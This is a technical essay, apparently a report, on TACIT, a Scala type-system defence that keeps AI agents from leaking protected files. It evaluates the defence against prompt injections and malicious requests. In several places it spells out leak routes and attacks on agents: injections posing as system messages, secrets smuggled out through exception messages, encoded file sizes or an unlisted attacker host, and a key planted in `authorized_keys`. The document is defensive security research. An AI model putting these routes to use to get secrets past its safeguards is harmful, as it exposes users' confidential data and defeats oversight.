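The double arrow is shorthand for an arrow that may capture anything. A function with a smaller capture set can replace one with a larger set, so a pure function can also be used wherever the program requires a double arrow.

Most Scala code already uses the double arrow, so existing code needs few changes. For instance, a list's `map` method, which applies a function to every element, takes an `A => B`, so it accepts any function, including one that writes to a file. A library author writes the single arrow only where a function must be pure, and the rest of the program can still read files and send mail.

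### The Classified wrapper

When a TACIT program reads a protected file, it gets a `Classified[String]` instead of a `String`. This is a sealed box with the text inside. Odersky and colleagues explain the idea with a box that has three methods:

```
class Classified[T] {
  def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
  def aggregate[U](other: Classified[U]): Classified[(T, U)]
  def reveal(using permission: CanAccess[T]): T
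}
```

`T` is the type of the content, and `U` can be any type.

The `map` method applies a function to the content and puts the result in a new box. Its parameter type and return type are both needed to prevent leaks. If `map` accepted a `T => U`, the agent could pass it a function that emails the contract. If it returned a plain `U`, the agent could get the contract out of the box by passing `x => x`, which returns its input unchanged.

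The `aggregate` method combines two boxes into one that contains a pair. The agent needs it to compare contracts, since `map` opens only one box. With the tools in the paper's example, which compare and summarise text, an agent could write the central steps of the contracts job in two lines:

```
val changes = oldText.aggregate(newText).map((a, b) => diff(a, b))
val summary = changes.map(text => summarize(text))
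```

The `reveal` method takes the content out of the box, but the caller must hold a `CanAccess` capability. The agent doesn't have one, though a user with the right clearance could hold one.

TACIT's actual library has `map` but replaces the other two methods, `aggregate` and `reveal`, with `flatMap`. This method takes a pure function that returns a box, and gives back a single box rather than a box inside a box. It can replace `aggregate`. For example, `a.flatMap(x => b.map(y => (x, y)))` puts the contents of `a` and `b` into one box. Because the library has no `reveal`, the user reads results on a separate channel that the agent can't see.

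### An accepted program and a rejected one

Suppose the user asks how long the summary is. The agent can write:

```
val length = summary.map(s => s.length)
```

The function refers only to its own input, so its capture set is empty and its type is `String -> Int`. `map` therefore accepts it and returns a `Classified[Int]`. If the agent prints the result, the agent sees `Classified(****)`, while the user sees the number.

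During the tests, an agent also tried to write classified text to a file from inside `map`. With its variables renamed, the code was essentially this:

```
summary.map { text =>
  outFile.write(text)
}
```

The compiler rejected it with a type error:

```
Found:    (text: String) ->{outFile} Unit
Required: String -> Unit
```

The error arises in four steps:

1. `outFile` is a file handle with a non-empty capture set, so the compiler treats it as a capability.
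2. The function's body uses `outFile`, which gives the function the type `String ->{outFile} Unit`.
3. The box contains a `String`, so `map` requires a function of type `String -> U`. The compiler sets `U` to `Unit`, because the function returns nothing useful.
4. The function would fit only if {`outFile`} <: {}. But `outFile` isn't in the empty set, and the empty set doesn't cover the file system from which `outFile` gets its power.

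The type rule forbids every write inside `map`, safe or not, and the compiler does not check where the file is. The path in the original code began with `secrets/`, so the text might not have left the protected area. The library also provides a `writeClassified` function, which takes the sealed box as a whole and checks at run time that the destination is a protected file.

A function captures whatever the functions it calls capture, so an agent can't hide the write in a helper function. It also can't copy the text into a variable outside the box, because Scala counts a mutable variable as a capability and a function that changes one isn't pure. Putting the file handle inside a pair can make the pair's type look pure, but the handle reappears in the capture set as soon as code takes it out to use it.

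### What a pure function can't do

Reading a file also requires a capability, so if a contract refers to an annex, a function inside `map` can't fetch the annex. This restriction is needed because someone who watches which files the program opens could learn what the contract says. The agent can instead read all the annexes first and let a pure function choose among the boxes.

The agent also has to write the function before seeing the text. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a later system from the same research group, addresses this by letting a program contain gaps that a model fills with code when execution reaches them. *LACUNA* puts such a gap inside the function passed to `map` and has a trusted local model fill it. The local model can read the contract and write code suited to it. The compiler checks this code under the same purity rule, so the code can't send the text anywhere.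 The cloud model still writes the surrounding program and never sees the contract.

### Capabilities that can't leave their block

An agent usually needs some access to files, but only to certain directories and for a limited time. TACIT grants it through a function with roughly this signature:

```
def requestFileSystem[T](root: String)(block: FileSystem^ => T): T
```

The function creates a file-system capability for one directory, passes it to a block of the agent's code, and returns the block's result. The capability is valid only while the block runs. The agent might try to keep it by returning a function that will read a file later:

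```
val later = requestFileSystem("/data") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("secret.txt").read()
}
```

The returned function uses `fs`, so its type is `() ->{fs} String`. But the result type `T` belongs to the code outside the block, where `fs` isn't in scope. The compiler looks for a more general type that doesn't mention `fs`, and the closest one is the type of a function that may capture anything. Scala doesn't let `T` stand for such a type, so it rejects the program. It also rejects attempts to store the function in an outside variable, or to hide it in another object and call it from there.

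The same rule can distinguish two programs that look almost identical. In an example from Scala's documentation, a program writes each element of a list to a log file as it computes the list. With an ordinary list, the writing finishes before the block ends, and the compiler accepts the program. A lazy list computes its elements only when the program uses them, possibly after the block has closed the file. The compiler rejects that version because the list still holds the file handle.

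Agents make this kind of mistake without malice. In one run that Odersky and colleagues report, the agent tried to return a list of file handles from the block, and the compiler stopped it. Plain text and `Classified` boxes can leave the block because they hold no capabilities.

This scoping also protects the secrets in the boxes. If a function inside `map` could call `requestFileSystem`, it could get a new file handle and write the contract to a file. Calling `requestFileSystem` therefore itself requires an input-output capability, which a pure function can't hold.

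### What the language must guarantee

Odersky and colleagues list three properties that the language must have for this protection to work:

- **Capability safety.** Code can't forge a capability or make the compiler forget that a value holds one. Otherwise, an agent could fabricate a `CanAccess` permission and open the box.
- **Capability completeness.** Every effect that matters for safety requires a capability, except those that the surrounding system can contain at run time. If a print function needed no capability, a function that printed the contract would count as pure.
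- **Local purity.** The type system can require that a particular computation uses only a stated set of capabilities, which may be empty.

Ordinary Scala lacks the first property, because programmers can discard capture sets with unchecked type conversions and similar features. TACIT compiles the agent's code in safe mode, a restricted version of the language. Mazur's *Scala 3.8.3 is now available!* describes safe mode as a new experimental feature.

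The second property depends on the library's author declaring the capabilities each tool uses. In a version of TACIT adapted for the AgentDojo benchmark, the published signature of the money-sending tool names no capability. The prompt for that version also warns the agent that side effects inside `map` happen immediately. These details suggest that the compiler would have accepted a bank transfer inside `map`, where the amount or recipient could depend on the protected data. The type checker would have worked correctly, but from an incomplete description of the tool.

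### Why the secret shouldn't affect what outsiders see

Odersky and colleagues say that these pure functions guarantee noninterference, but they don't set out a proof. One could argue for this claim as follows.

Run the same program twice, with contract text *s* the first time and *s′* the second, and keep everything else the same. Call the two runs equivalent at some point if they differ only in what is inside the boxes. They are equivalent at the start. There are then two kinds of step to consider:

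- Code outside the boxes can't inspect their contents. It therefore does the same thing in both runs, with the same visible effects.
- A call to `map` with a pure function *f* produces a box containing *f*(*s*) in one run and *f*(*s′*) in the other. Computing these values has no outside effect, and the results stay in boxes.

Each step leaves the runs equivalent, so by induction they stay equivalent to the end. An outside observer therefore sees the same actions in both runs and learns nothing about the contract.

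This covers implicit flows as well as explicit ones. In TACIT, the agent described earlier, which notifies the legal department only when a penalty clause has changed, can work out whether the clause has changed, but the answer is a `Classified[Boolean]`, a true-or-false value in a box. Code can branch on that value only inside `map`, where it can't send mail. The agent can still send the same message whether or not the clause has changed, or show the answer to an authorised person, but it can't make the message depend on the clause.

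FIDES blocks only explicit flows, so it may allow the notification. TACIT's stronger guarantee rules out any task in which a secret has to determine a publicly visible action, including useful ones.

The argument relies on the three language properties. It also assumes that the box reveals nothing about its contents, for instance through an equality test that compares the contents of two boxes, and that outsiders cannot read the places where the library delivers protected results. It does not account for how long a pure function takes or whether it finishes.

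It also assumes that the tools the compiler treats as pure are pure. The summarising tool counts as pure because its type lists no capabilities, but it sends the contract to another language model. If that model's operator logged the text, or the model used it in answering a later request, the program would still pass the type check. Odersky and colleagues therefore leave it to the system's builders to make sure that the model keeps no memory of earlier requests.

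### What researchers have proved

Researchers usually prove results about a type system by studying a calculus, a small language with only the features they need. A type system is sound if programs that pass its checks never behave in ways the types rule out. A proof is mechanised if a computer program has checked every step.

*A Mechanized Theory of the Box Calculus* (2023) noted that one version of the calculus behind capture checking had been fully mechanised, but that the soundness proofs for other versions had not. Odersky and colleagues now describe the soundness of the base type system as mechanised, citing *What's in the Box* (2025) and an earlier paper. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) adds a way to restrict capabilities by kind instead of one by one, and proves type and effect safety for the extended calculus in the proof-checking language Lean.

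In *System Capybara*, Xu, Bračevac and colleagues (2026) present the result closest to local purity. They interpret a capture set as the memory locations that code may read, change or free, and prove in Lean that a well-typed program touches only those locations and any it creates. A function with an empty capture set therefore can't touch memory that existed before it ran, unless it receives access to that memory as an input.

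This still isn't a proof about TACIT. The calculus leaves out classes and exceptions, and its only effects are operations on memory, with no files or networks. Xu and colleagues also don't prove that the Scala compiler implements the calculus correctly. They use "non-interference" to mean that two computations don't make conflicting use of the same memory, which is a different property from keeping secrets.

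Odersky and colleagues say that a semantic soundness proof is still needed to show that safe mode provides capability safety and local purity. Such a proof would define what the types mean in terms of how programs run, as the Capybara proof does. Noninterference for `Classified` would still need its own proof, because noninterference compares two runs with different secrets, while the existing soundness theorems concern what a program may do in a single run.

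### Earlier ways to control flows with types

The idea of recording effects in types goes back to the 1980s. Lucassen and Gifford (1988), in *Polymorphic Effect Systems*, gave each expression a type and an effect that described how the expression might read or change memory. A compiler could use these effects to find computations that were safe to run in parallel. Capture checking can be seen as an effect system whose effects are the capabilities a value holds.

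Another line of work put secrecy labels into types. *JFlow* (Myers, 1999) extended Java with labels that name the owners of data and the readers each owner permits. The compiler checks most flows before the program runs. It also tracks implicit flows by labelling each part of the program according to the secrets that determine whether it runs.

In the same year, Abadi, Banerjee and colleagues published *A Core Calculus of Dependency*, which has a type much like `Classified` for every level of a lattice. A value of type A protected at level ℓ has type T<sub>ℓ</sub>(A). A program may use the protected value to compute something else only if the result is also protected at ℓ or higher. A result of type T<sub>m</sub>(B), for example, is allowed if ℓ ⊑ m. The paper includes a proof of noninterference for the calculus. `Classified` with `map` and `flatMap` is close to the special case with a single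 protected level, but the calculus doesn't include operations on files or email.

Functions in the Haskell language are pure by default, which made it possible to build such boxes as a library. *A Library for Light-Weight Information-Flow Security in Haskell* (Russo, Claessen and Hughes, 2008) presents one in which the type of each protected value includes its security level. LIO, a later Haskell library by Stefan, Russo and colleagues (2011), instead checks labels while the program runs. It keeps a current label that rises as the program reads protected data, and blocks writes to places where that data may not go. FIDES treats an agent's context in much the same way.

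*Cocoon* (Lamba and colleagues, 2024) does something similar in Rust, a language whose functions can have side effects anywhere. It lets programmers handle secrets only in marked blocks of code, and uses Rust's existing type system and macros to check that these blocks have no side effects. *Carapace* (Beardsley and colleagues, 2025) extends this approach with integrity labels and labels chosen at run time.

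Pure functions on sealed data were well established before TACIT. Tracked capabilities add a way to combine these functions with ordinary code that has side effects, while still tracking individual permissions. Haskell can separate pure functions from the rest, but Odersky and colleagues point out that it has no built-in object capabilities, so programmers would have to encode access to a particular file in more complicated types. Older capability languages, such as E and Joe-E, control access while a program runs but can't express in a type that a function holds no capabilities. Scala can do both, and can also limit how long a permission lasts.

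The checking takes fairly little time because the compiler can examine each function using the types of the functions it calls, without analysing the whole program at once. *What's in the Box* reports that capture checking took less than 15% of total compilation time for Scala's standard library.

### One level of secrecy

`Classified` marks data as protected but doesn't record who may read it. FIDES could label the summary of the two contracts with its permitted readers, {Bob, Cem}, and let the agent email it to Bob. In TACIT, the summary is a `Classified[String]` and the email tool takes an ordinary `String`, so the agent can't send the summary to anyone, including Bob.

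A single level can also be too permissive. TACIT lets the agent write the summary to any protected file it can access. If Dana can open that file, she can read a summary that draws on a contract she isn't allowed to see. The type checker accepts this because the source and the destination are both classified.

The `CanAccess[T]` permission in the paper's design does not solve this, because `T` describes the form of the content, not where it came from. A firm could give each contract its own type and issue a separate permission for each. But once the agent uses `map` to extract a contract's text, the result is a `Classified[String]`, and anyone with permission to reveal classified strings can open it.

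A more expressive version would add a label to the type, as the Haskell library and the dependency calculus do. `Classified[L, T]` could mean content of type `T` with label `L`. Then `map` would keep the label, and `aggregate` would take the join of two labels:

Classified[L, T] and Classified[M, U] → Classified[L ⊔ M, (T, U)]

If `L` and `M` were the readers of the two contracts, the pair would have the label {Bob, Cem}, and an email tool could require every recipient to be on that list.

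A compiler may not know in advance who is allowed to read a piece of data. An agent may not learn who can open a document until it fetches the document, or who is on a mailing list until it looks the list up. FIDES can handle this because it compares labels at run time. A typed system would need to combine its compile-time check with a run-time one, as JFlow and Carapace do.

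## What must surround the type checker for the guarantee to hold?

The compiler can protect the contracts only from code it checks. TACIT therefore needs other software to send the agent's actions to the compiler, run the accepted code and control how much of the results the agent sees. A mistake in this software, or in how a firm sets it up, can reveal a contract even if the type checker works perfectly.

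### One request through TACIT

TACIT is a server that uses the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to tools. The agent can be an existing product, such as Claude Code or GitHub Copilot. A request goes through these steps:

1. The agent writes a piece of Scala code and sends it to the server as the argument of a tool call.
2. The server adds a few lines that make TACIT's library available, and compiles the code in safe mode.
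3. If the compiler finds an error, nothing runs. The agent gets the error message and can correct the code.
4. Otherwise, the server runs the code in an interactive Scala session, which can keep the code's variables for later requests.
5. Whenever the code needs a file, another program or the network, it calls the library. The library checks at run time that the path, command or host is a permitted one.
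6. The server returns the code's output to the agent.

These steps protect nothing if the agent can bypass them. If Claude Code opens a contract with its own file-reading or command-running tools, the text goes straight into the cloud model's context. *TACIT*, the documentation published with the code by lampepfl, a research group at the Swiss university EPFL, recommends switching off the agent's built-in file, shell and network tools. The user has to do this in the agent's own settings.

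### What safe mode forbids

Scala's *Safe Mode* lists six restrictions. Each one closes a way to hide a capability or to cause an effect that the types don't show:

| Restriction | What code could do without it |
|---|---|
| No unchecked type casts or pattern matches | Pass off a function that writes to a file as a pure one |
| No features from the `caps.unsafe` module | Stop the compiler from tracking changes to a variable |
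| No `@unchecked` annotations | Switch off checks for a particular expression |
| No runtime reflection | Look up a method by name during the run and call it without the compiler's knowledge |
| Capture checking on, including for changes to variables | Copy a secret from a supposedly pure function into an outside variable |
| Only global objects that are themselves safe | Call a library function that has side effects but requires no capability |

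The last restriction also applies to Scala's standard library. The compiler's developers have approved most of the main `scala` package but not its global print functions, so TACIT supplies its own `println`, which requires a capability.

At first, TACIT enforced some of this with a separate validator that searched the agent's code for forbidden patterns. lampepfl described this validator and planned to replace it with the compiler's safe mode. A pattern search catches only the patterns listed in advance, while the compiler works out what each expression refers to. Glama's *TACIT*, a later copy of the documentation in a directory of agent tools, describes safe mode as on by default in one passage and as an optional addition to the pattern search in another. A firm would therefore do well to turn safe mode on explicitly.

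### Two outputs and a second model

When the agent's code prints a `Classified` value, the user sees the content but the agent sees only `Classified(****)`. Both see the same text when the code prints an ordinary value.

The agent can't read the contracts, so a second model, which the firm trusts, does any work that requires understanding them. The agent's code calls this model through a function named `chat`. If the code passes `chat` an ordinary `String`, it gets an ordinary `String` back. If it passes a `Classified[String]`, the trusted model can read the text inside, and the answer comes back as a new `Classified[String]`. As in Willison's pattern, an instruction hidden in a contract can distort the answer but can't trigger a tool call.

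The contracts job might run over two turns of a conversation as follows, in an adaptation of an example by Odersky and colleagues. The user first asks what has changed, and the agent writes:

```
val summary = requestFileSystem("/contracts") {
  val oldText = readClassified("old.txt")
  val newText = readClassified("new.txt")
  val both = oldText.flatMap(a => newText.map(b => s"OLD: $a NEW: $b"))
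  chat("Summarise what has changed.", both)
}
println(summary)
```

The user sees the summary, and the agent sees `Classified(****)`. The user then asks whether the penalty clause is among the changes:

```
val answer = chat("Has the penalty clause changed?", summary)
println(answer)
```

Again, only the user sees the answer. The session has kept `summary` in its box, so the agent doesn't need to reopen the contracts. Its permission to open files ended with the `requestFileSystem` block in the first turn, so it would have to request permission again to read them.

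The agent never sees the results, so it can't notice that a summary is empty or obviously wrong, or use an answer to decide on its next step. The user could type the answer into the chat, but that would send it to the cloud provider.

### The parts that must work

The trusted computing base of a system consists of the parts that must work correctly for its guarantee to hold. In TACIT, these are the main ones:

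| Part | What can happen if it is wrong |
|---|---|
| Compiler | It accepts a function as pure although the function sends text out |
| Library, including code that its authors mark as safe | A tool has an effect that its type doesn't declare |
| Runtime | Code breaks out of the session, or an error message carries a secret to the agent |
| Trusted model | Its operator stores the contracts or passes them on |
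| List of classified folders | A contract arrives as ordinary text, which the agent can print |

Odersky and colleagues say the reusable part of the library is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and the wrappers for each new set of tools add a few hundred. The compiler is far larger, and capture checking and safe mode are still experimental. The researchers also suggest running TACIT in a sandbox, in case code escapes the runtime.

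An administrator selects the trusted model by entering a web address, and TACIT accepts any service compatible with OpenAI's interface. The types don't require the model to be local. If the address belongs to a cloud service, the agent's programs will still pass the type check and will send the contracts there.

The list of folders is just as easy to get wrong. According to Glama's copy of the documentation, TACIT by default classifies common locations for credentials, such as `.ssh` and `.env`. The administrator has to list any other folder, such as the one where a firm keeps its contracts. If the administrator leaves that folder out, or an employee saves a copy of a contract somewhere else, the library returns the contract as a plain `String`. The defaults apply only when the administrator has set no list, so a firm that lists just its contracts folder may lose the protection for its credentials.

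Output printed for the user can also leak secrets to the agent. In the later version, TACIT can write this output to a file, which the sample configuration places in `/tmp`. The same configuration lets the agent open files in `/tmp`, and none of its classified patterns match the output file. Unless the library blocks that file in some other way, the agent could read every secret that earlier code had printed for the user.

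`Classified` also doesn't stop an agent from damaging protected files. Any code can put its own text in a box and write it to a classified path. Glama's copy gives the example of `.ssh/authorized_keys`, which lists who may log in to a computer. An attacker who got an agent to add a key there might log in and read the contracts directly. Administrators can prevent this by turning off writes to classified paths.

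### Mistakes in the library

Library authors sometimes need features that safe mode forbids. For example, a function that stores earlier results to save time has to change a variable. The author can mark such code `@assumeSafe`, and the compiler then lets agents call it even though it hasn't checked the implementation. The author must therefore make sure that the code's side effects can't be seen from outside. Agents can't use this mark in their own code, according to *Safe Scala an introduction* by the software company VirtusLab.

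One of Scala's examples of the mark is `CheckedMailer`, an object that asks the user for confirmation and then sends an email. The outline declares no capability for sending mail, so it seems that a function inside `map` could call `CheckedMailer` and put a contract in the email. The only remaining protection would be the user reading the message before clicking "OK".

The library interface that Odersky and colleagues published seems to have had a more serious gap. An agent is supposed to get a `Network` object by calling `requestNetwork`, which it can't do inside `map`. But the published `Network` class has a public constructor, so any code can create one. A function inside `map` could apparently have created its own `Network` object and used it to send a contract to any server. The compiler would still have counted the function as pure, because a function's capture set lists only capabilities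 from outside the function. Another check may have prevented this in practice. In the later version that Glama describes, only the library can create capability objects.

File names and sizes may also be unprotected. The library returns the text of a classified file in a box, but the published interface gives a file's name as an ordinary `String` and its size as an ordinary number. If this holds for classified files too, an agent can list the contracts folder and print a name such as `termination-of-supplier.docx`.

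File sizes could reveal much more, because the agent can also write classified files. It could use a pure function to turn the first letter of a contract into a string whose length encodes that letter, save the string in a classified file and ask for the file's size. It could recover the whole contract by repeating this for each letter, and the type checker would accept every step. The library could prevent this by putting sizes in boxes too, or by refusing to report them for classified files.

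### Exceptions

Safe mode lets code throw exceptions, which are errors that interrupt a program. Throwing one requires no capability, so the compiler would accept this line:

```
newText.map(text => throw new Exception(text))
```

If the server passed the error message on to the agent, the agent would receive the contract in it. A function could also reveal a single fact by failing only when the contract has a penalty clause.

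Scala's designers decided not to track exceptions in types because almost any code can cause one, for instance by dividing by zero or running out of memory. Instead, the caller guards against exceptions at run time by wrapping untrusted code in `Try`, a standard Scala class that turns an exception into an ordinary value. The caller can then put that value in a box. This also covers other ways of leaving a function early, such as breaking out of a loop, because Scala 3 represents them all as exceptions.

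Hiding errors makes the agent's work harder. In the version of TACIT for the AgentDojo benchmark, the library hides any exception thrown inside `map`, including its message. The agent sees no error and the user gets an empty result, so the code seems to have worked. The prompt therefore tells the agent to return an explanation for the user, such as "No matching transaction", instead of throwing an exception.

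### Outside commands and permitted hosts

When the agent's code starts another program, the compiler can't check what that program does. The remaining protection is the list of commands the agent may run. An outside program can normally open any file that the user running it can open, and TACIT returns the program's output as ordinary text. If the list included `cat`, which prints a file, the agent could use it to read a contract.

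Odersky and colleagues recommend permitting only specific safe commands, and give `git diff` and the build tool `sbt` as examples. `sbt` is a doubtful choice because its build files can contain arbitrary code. An agent that can edit those files and run `sbt` can therefore run any code.

In the later version, code can also send the content of a box to a permitted web host. This lets an agent log in to a service with a password it can't see, but the firm now has to trust every permitted host. According to Glama's copy, the administrator's list of hosts is optional. Without it, the only limit is the list that the agent's own code passes to `requestNetwork`. As documented, an agent could then name an attacker's server and send it a contract. The program would type-check because the library treats the transfer as legitimate.

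### Checking before the run or during it

TACIT's compiler rejects a leaking program before any of it runs. CaMeL's interpreter checks each tool call just before making it, so it may have made several calls before it reaches one that the policy forbids.

A type check also covers every text that a contract might contain, so the compiler has to reject code that could leak even if it wouldn't do so this time. A run-time check like CaMeL's covers only the current run, but it can look up who may read a particular contract, then allow an email to Bob and refuse one to Dana.

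CaMeL's programs can't define their own functions, while TACIT's agents can use nearly all of Scala. Odersky and colleagues argue that it would be hard to lift CaMeL's restriction and still give guarantees before a program runs. An analysis may need exponential time to predict precisely where data can flow through arbitrary functions. Scala avoids this problem because each function's type already states which capabilities the function holds. However, an interpreter that labels values as the program runs can track them through a function as easily as through any other code, without predicting where they will go. Run-time tracking therefore doesn't seem to require CaMeL's restriction.

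TACIT checks paths, commands and hosts at run time. Odersky and colleagues see the two approaches as complementary, and suggest that the library could also run checks before releasing data, keep logs and limit how often an agent uses a tool.

### Do labels survive a conversation?

Odersky and colleagues also criticise CaMeL for losing track of data in conversation. They argue that a value loses its label once it enters the model's conversation as ordinary text, because nothing records which of the model's later words came from that value.

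This should rarely matter within a single CaMeL program, because the interpreter keeps results in labelled variables. The problem arises between programs. Suppose the first program shows the user a summary of a contract, and the summary stays in the conversation. The user then says, "Send that to Dana." If the main model copies the summary into its next program, the interpreter will presumably treat it as the model's own text, with no restriction on who may read it.

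FIDES avoids this because it labels the context as a whole. Once the summary is in the context, an email to Dana would violate the permitted-flow policy. So the criticism applies to systems that label only the values in a program, not to run-time tracking in general. Labelling the whole context causes label creep, however.

TACIT has no labels for the conversation either. It relies on keeping classified text out of it, and has no other protection if some gets in. If the user pastes the summary into the chat, the agent can put it in an email as an ordinary `String`, and the compiler will accept the program.

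### LACUNA's gaps in a program

In TACIT, an ordinary agent loop runs outside the type system and submits pieces of code for checking. LACUNA moves the loop into the program. Zhao and colleagues add a function that stands for a gap in the code:

```
def agent[T](task: String): T
```

`T` is the type of result that the surrounding code needs. LACUNA fills the gap as follows:

1. When the run reaches the gap, LACUNA sends the model the task, the required type, the surrounding code, and the variables and functions available there.
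2. The model returns Scala code.
3. The compiler checks the code as if a programmer had written it at that point.
4. If the code passes, it runs and its result fills the gap. If it fails, LACUNA sends the model the errors and lets it try again, up to a set limit.

The new code can contain further gaps. A model can therefore use ordinary program code to split a task into parts, repeat a step or hand work to another model. It could also keep creating gaps forever, so LACUNA lets users limit how deeply gaps can be nested.

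The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. In one example, the model has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new number. It writes code that subtracts correctly but returns a sentence instead of a number. The compiler rejects the code, so the balance stays at 100 and the model can safely try again. A Python system that found the error only during the run would already have changed the balance on the first attempt.

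A gap's position also determines what its code may do. The programmer can make a file available at one gap and the network at another, and the code in each can use only what is available there. A hostile web page may still cause the model to write harmful code, but that code gets no extra permissions.

This doesn't help if the attacker can use a permission that the task needs. When Zhao and colleagues ran AgentDojo's attacks against LACUNA with two models, 8 of 1,898 succeeded. They note that the type system enforces the limits a developer sets but can't determine what those limits should be.

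With LACUNA, the trusted computing base also includes the machinery that compiles new code inside a running program. Zhao and colleagues tested it on about 400 combinations of surrounding and generated code, and all gave the expected result. They based these tests on mistakes that agents commonly make, so the results are weaker evidence of protection against an attacker looking for a combination nobody considered.

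LACUNA solved fewer tasks than an ordinary tool-calling agent on τ²-bench, a benchmark of simulated customer-service conversations, although the paper's abstract calls it "on par". With the model DeepSeek V4 Flash, LACUNA solved 76.0% of 392 tasks and the ordinary agent solved 90.0%. With the weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, the figures were 29.1% and 33.2%.

### Complete agents built on TACIT

Developers have since built complete agents around TACIT. Glama's copy describes ATC (Agent with Tracked Capabilities), a coding agent that denies access by default and lets the user grant permissions temporarily or for one session. Users don't have to connect a separate agent, so they shouldn't have to switch off that agent's own tools either.

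EPFL and VirtusLab are working on CapybaraClaw, an agent meant to run permanently. In *Making the AI agents safe with Scala*, Biały and Warchoł (2026) announced a talk on it for October 2026 and promised to share material from exercises that used frontier AI models to look for ways to break TACIT. The results of such attacks would be better evidence about the compiler and library than the developers' own tests of intended behaviour.

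A permanent agent will often need a web browser, which TACIT's original library didn't cover. *AI on your desktop* (Scala Days, 2026), the description of another conference talk, warns that an agent could open local files in a browser, or take a screenshot of a confidential document and send it to a cloud model. The speakers propose a browser capability limited to particular sites, with pages and screenshots in `Classified` boxes. They expect to add it in under 30 lines of code, without changing the type checker.

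## Does typed code stop leaks in tests, and what does it cost in completed work?

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a project folder containing secrets, on AgentDojo's simulated accounts, and on ordinary benchmark tasks that involved no secrets. They designed only the first test to detect leaks.

### The leak test

The agent worked on a sample software project. One folder held API keys (passwords that programs use to access a service), a database and confidential documents. An untrusted cloud model, either Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 4.6 or MiniMax M2.5, ran the agent, and a trusted local model could read the secrets.

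The test used 12 legitimate tasks. Some didn't involve the secrets, such as listing the web addresses described in a README file. Others required them, such as summarising a classified incident report or anonymising employee reviews. Each task ran once with each of 10 injections, for a total of 120 trials. The simplest injections were instructions in developer notes or code comments. Others were disguised as system messages, faked an error that only credentials could fix, or claimed that the secrets were synthetic test data. Some included finished Scala code for reading the secret files.

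In another 11 trials, the user was the attacker. The user asked for secrets outright in five trials and used a pretext in the other six, such as an administrator's urgent need to replace credentials.

Every trial ran once with the secrets in `Classified` boxes and once with them as ordinary text. A trial counted as secure if no secret content appeared in the agent's output.

| Model | Trials | Secure with `Classified` | Secure without |
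|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 with injections | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | all 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 with injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | all 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

Without the boxes, Sonnet leaked secrets in two trials, both using a pretext. MiniMax leaked them in 11 trials, three with injections and eight with malicious requests. With the boxes, the compiler stopped programs that would have leaked. In one, the agent opened a GitHub key and tried to print it from inside `map`.

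The boxes did not reduce the number of legitimate tasks completed. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the 120 trials with them and 83.3% without, and MiniMax completed 90.0% and 88.3%. It is odd that a restriction helped Sonnet, and Odersky and colleagues suggest that its lower figure without the boxes may be an artefact of the set-up. Sonnet tends to do more work on each task, so it often ran out of turns or time. When it detected an injection, it sometimes stopped to warn the user instead of finishing the task.

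This could explain why Sonnet did worse than MiniMax without the boxes, but not why the boxes helped, because the agent could read an injection in a code comment with or without them. Perhaps Sonnet was more cautious when it could see real-looking credentials. The result is at best weak evidence that `Classified` makes agents more useful.

### How much 131 trials can show

Sonnet resisted all 120 injections without types, so those trials can't show that types protected it. The whole measured benefit of types for Sonnet comes from two of the 11 malicious requests. The effect on MiniMax is much clearer, but 11 requests is a small set, and the people who wrote them also built the defence.

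The test also compares TACIT with no protection. A rule against opening the secrets folder would have stopped the direct requests too, but would have made the incident summary impossible. A comparison with run-time labels on the same folder would better show what types add.

No data leaked in 262 protected trials. Even if these were independent random samples of attacks, the true leak rate could still be about 1%. They aren't random samples, and a real attacker would look for whatever works. The main argument for TACIT's security is therefore still the type rule. The trials show that the compiler and library enforced that rule on the code that two models happened to write.

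As the paper describes them, none of the injections targets the library's own weak points, such as the file sizes it may report for classified files. The scoring might have missed such a leak anyway, because a search for secret content in the agent's output would not normally flag a list of file sizes, even if someone could decode a contract from it.

### AgentDojo, setting by setting

Odersky and colleagues also adapted AgentDojo's four settings to TACIT without changing the tasks or attacks. They compared the results with published CaMeL results for the same models, Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro and OpenAI's o4-mini at high reasoning effort. Zhao and colleagues later added LACUNA. The table gives the percentage of tasks completed:

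| Model and system | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | 52.8 | 53.8 | 48.6 | 1.4 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT | 56.9 | 50.5 | 40.0 | 64.3 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, LACUNA | 63.2 | 56.3 | 42.9 | 63.6 |
| o4-mini, CaMeL | 62.5 | 81.4 | 68.6 | 74.3 |
| o4-mini, TACIT | 59.0 | 52.9 | 47.6 | 68.6 |
| o4-mini, LACUNA | 66.0 | 55.5 | 49.5 | 71.4 |

These results seem to come from runs under attack. Slack's 40.0% matches 42 of its 105 attack runs, while no whole number of its 21 user tasks gives that percentage.

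Odersky and colleagues describe TACIT's utility as comparable to CaMeL's. That is fair for Gemini in banking, the workspace and Slack, where the gaps were 3 to 9 points and neither system was always ahead. With o4-mini, TACIT was behind CaMeL in all four settings, by 28.5 points in the workspace and 21 in Slack.

With Gemini, CaMeL completed only two of 140 travel runs (1.4%), which makes averages for that model misleading. Over all four settings, TACIT averages 53% and CaMeL 39%. Without travel, CaMeL leads by 52% to 49%. CaMeL completed 74.3% of the travel runs with o4-mini, so the tasks were not too hard for it. Something probably went wrong in how CaMeL worked with Gemini, but Odersky and colleagues don't say what.

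Switching from Gemini to o4-mini raised CaMeL's workspace score by 28 points and TACIT's by only 2. TACIT's interface may have limited its score. In the workspace and Slack versions, nearly every tool that reads data returns a box, and even the list of Slack channels is classified. In travel, where TACIT did best, the agent can see prices, addresses and flight times, and only reviews and calendar entries are in boxes.

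CaMeL also hides tool outputs from its main model, so hiding data can't be the whole explanation. However, CaMeL can pass a hidden value to a tool if a policy allows the call, whereas TACIT's tools for taking action accept only ordinary values.

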